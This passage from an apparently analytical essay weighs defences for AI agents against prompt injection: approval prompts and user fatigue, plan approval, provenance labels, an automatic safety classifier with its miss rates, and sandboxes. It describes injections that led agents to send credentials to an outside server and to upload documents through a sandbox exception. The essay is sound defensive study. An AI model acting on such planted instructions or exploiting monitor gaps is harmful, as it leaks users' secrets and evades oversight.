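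The sample is large enough that chance alone would move the 13.6% by only about two points either way. A bigger limitation is that the testers were not working on their own projects, so they had less to lose than a developer with real passwords and customers. Anthropic also published the result to support making auto mode the default. It doesn't report whether it chose the point in the session at random, so the drop from 17% to 5% might partly reflect differences between people who had long and short sessions.

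The study also doesn't show how people would respond to an approval request from CaMeL or FIDES. Users could see fewer requests with these systems, which should help. But the study's planted commands were obviously dangerous, while an attacker's email address may look just like Bob's. To catch the attack, the user would have to know the right address or check it elsewhere.

### How often to ask

For an attack that can succeed only if the user approves a prompt:

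chance of harm = chance that the attack reaches a prompt × chance that the user approves it

A strict system can reduce the number of attacks that reach an approval request by refusing some calls outright and keeping untrusted text away from the planner. But if it also asks users to approve many legitimate actions, they may pay less attention and become more likely to approve an attack.

In the table below, the approval rates for testers come from Anthropic's early and late results. The other inputs are invented for illustration.

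| User and policy | Attack reaches a prompt | User approves | Chance of harm |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tester, few prompts | 20% | 83% | 16.6% |
| Tester, many prompts | 10% | 95% | 9.5% |
| Careful user, few prompts | 20% | 20% | 4% |
| Careful user, many prompts | 10% | 60% | 6% |

The stricter policy halves the number of attacks that reach either user. This helps the tester, who would have approved most of them. For the careful user, it raises the chance of harm by half, because fatigue removes more protection than the policy adds. At the testers' approval rates, a stricter policy has to reduce the number of attacks that reach the user by about an eighth to keep the chance of harm from rising.

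The formula leaves out harmful calls that a policy allows without asking, which are more common under a loose policy. It also assumes that each attack leads to a single approval prompt. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of how software practitioners make permission decisions, points out that agents often look for another way to do something after a refusal. If an attack led to two separate prompts and the user had a 13.6% chance of catching each, the chance of approving at least one would be about 98%.

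Untrusted content can also influence what the user sees and believes when approving an action. Users may therefore approve a deliberate attack more often than an agent's accidental mistake.

### Earlier questions and whole plans

A system can reduce this influence by asking the user before the agent reads any untrusted data, as COBRA does when a request leaves out a sensitive value. Wang, Li and Tian recommend this more generally, because users are already thinking about the task when they write the request. They have not tested it with users, and COBRA's test used simulated answers. Someone who wants an agent to find a meeting request can't supply its date in advance, but they could limit the agent to meetings with colleagues during working hours, a limit that ordinary code can check.

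Another option is to ask users to approve a whole plan instead of each action. Anthropic found that Claude Code users reject 39% of plans but only 3% of individual permission requests. This suggests that people examine plans more closely, although they may reject many plans because they want a different technical approach. A test comparable to the tester study would hide a harmful step in a plan and measure how many people notice it.

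Plan approval also has a weakness when tasks depend on untrusted data. The user approves the plan for Bob's document before the agent opens the meeting notes that contain the address. The user can confirm that the document should go to the address in the notes, but can't check the address itself. Approving the plan therefore helps with control-flow integrity but doesn't solve the data-flow problem.

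### Showing where values came from

For the calendar event, a more informative prompt could show the date and each guest's address, and mark them all as coming from a stranger's email. Microsoft has asked developers for ideas on how FIDES could better explain why approval is needed. Wang, Li and Tian reviewed 21 production systems and found none that shows trust labels to users. They think the main obstacle is that people do not naturally think about data in those terms.

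Wu and colleagues' survey gives some indirect support for showing users something concrete to check. For four of seven types of sensitive action, developers who inspect diffs, which show exactly what changed in the code, reported approving without close review less often than other developers did. But they may just be more careful people. *Let the Agent Do It?* warns that more transparency does not always make oversight easier. Showing the source of a value would probably help most when the source is surprising, and in Bob's case the user already expects the address to come from the notes.

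### Fewer prompts and automatic review

Many people similarly ignored browser warnings about unsafe websites. Wang, Li and Tian note that simpler wording, fewer warnings and safer defaults later improved how people responded. For agents, the simplest way to reduce approval prompts is to let users permanently allow an action, but these permissions tend to accumulate, and only two of the 21 systems offered any way to narrow them. Systems can also learn permissions from past approvals, but people may have clicked through those prompts out of habit or time pressure.

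Auto mode replaces most of Claude Code's approval prompts with a classifier. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains that the classifier reads the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or tool results. Text injected into a web page therefore can't reach the classifier directly. In early tests, the classifier wrongly blocked 0.4% of ordinary actions and missed 17% of 52 real cases in which an agent had gone beyond what the user authorised. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier identified the action as dangerous but misclassified it as authorised by the user.

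Hiding tool results also prevents the classifier from checking where a value came from. If the agent cancels job "abc123", the classifier can't determine whether the agent found that name in a query or made it up. Labels like those in FIDES could identify the value's source without exposing the classifier to the untrusted text.

In an outside evaluation commissioned by Anthropic, none of 720 injection attempts succeeded against three Claude models running in auto mode. But even without permission checks, the average success rate against Anthropic's latest models was 0.09%, so the test is little help in judging how much protection auto mode adds. In tests by Apollo Research, an AI safety company, auto mode's classifier missed 12% of synthetic attacks at first and 7% after Anthropic improved it. Auto mode is a probabilistic defense, and Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes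 changes to live systems themselves.

### Sandboxes

A sandbox limits which files and servers a program can reach, whatever commands it runs. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) describes one for Claude Code that lets the agent work freely inside these limits and asks the user for approval only when the agent tries to cross them. The sandbox has to restrict both files and the network. An agent with unrestricted network access could send out any secret it can read, and one with unrestricted file access could alter the system to escape the network restriction.

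This sandbox reduced permission prompts by 84%. That should leave users with more attention for each remaining prompt, but Anthropic has not published a test of whether they catch more attacks.

Sandboxes can also protect users who would have approved the attack. In an internal exercise in February 2026, an Anthropic researcher persuaded an employee to run a prompt with instructions to send login credentials to an outside server. Claude sent them in 24 of 25 repetitions. Someone who trusted the prompt might well have approved each step, but a network restriction would have blocked the transfer.

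The limits themselves can have gaps. The sandbox for Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, had to permit connections to Anthropic's own servers. This exception let a malicious file make the agent upload the user's documents to an attacker's Anthropic account. Anthropic then added a check that accepts only requests made with the user's own session credentials.

Sandboxes work well for coding because an agent can do much of its work inside one folder. But adding a meeting or sending someone a document always affects something outside the sandbox. If the guest list or the recipient's address comes from untrusted text, the system still has to refuse, trust the text or ask the user.
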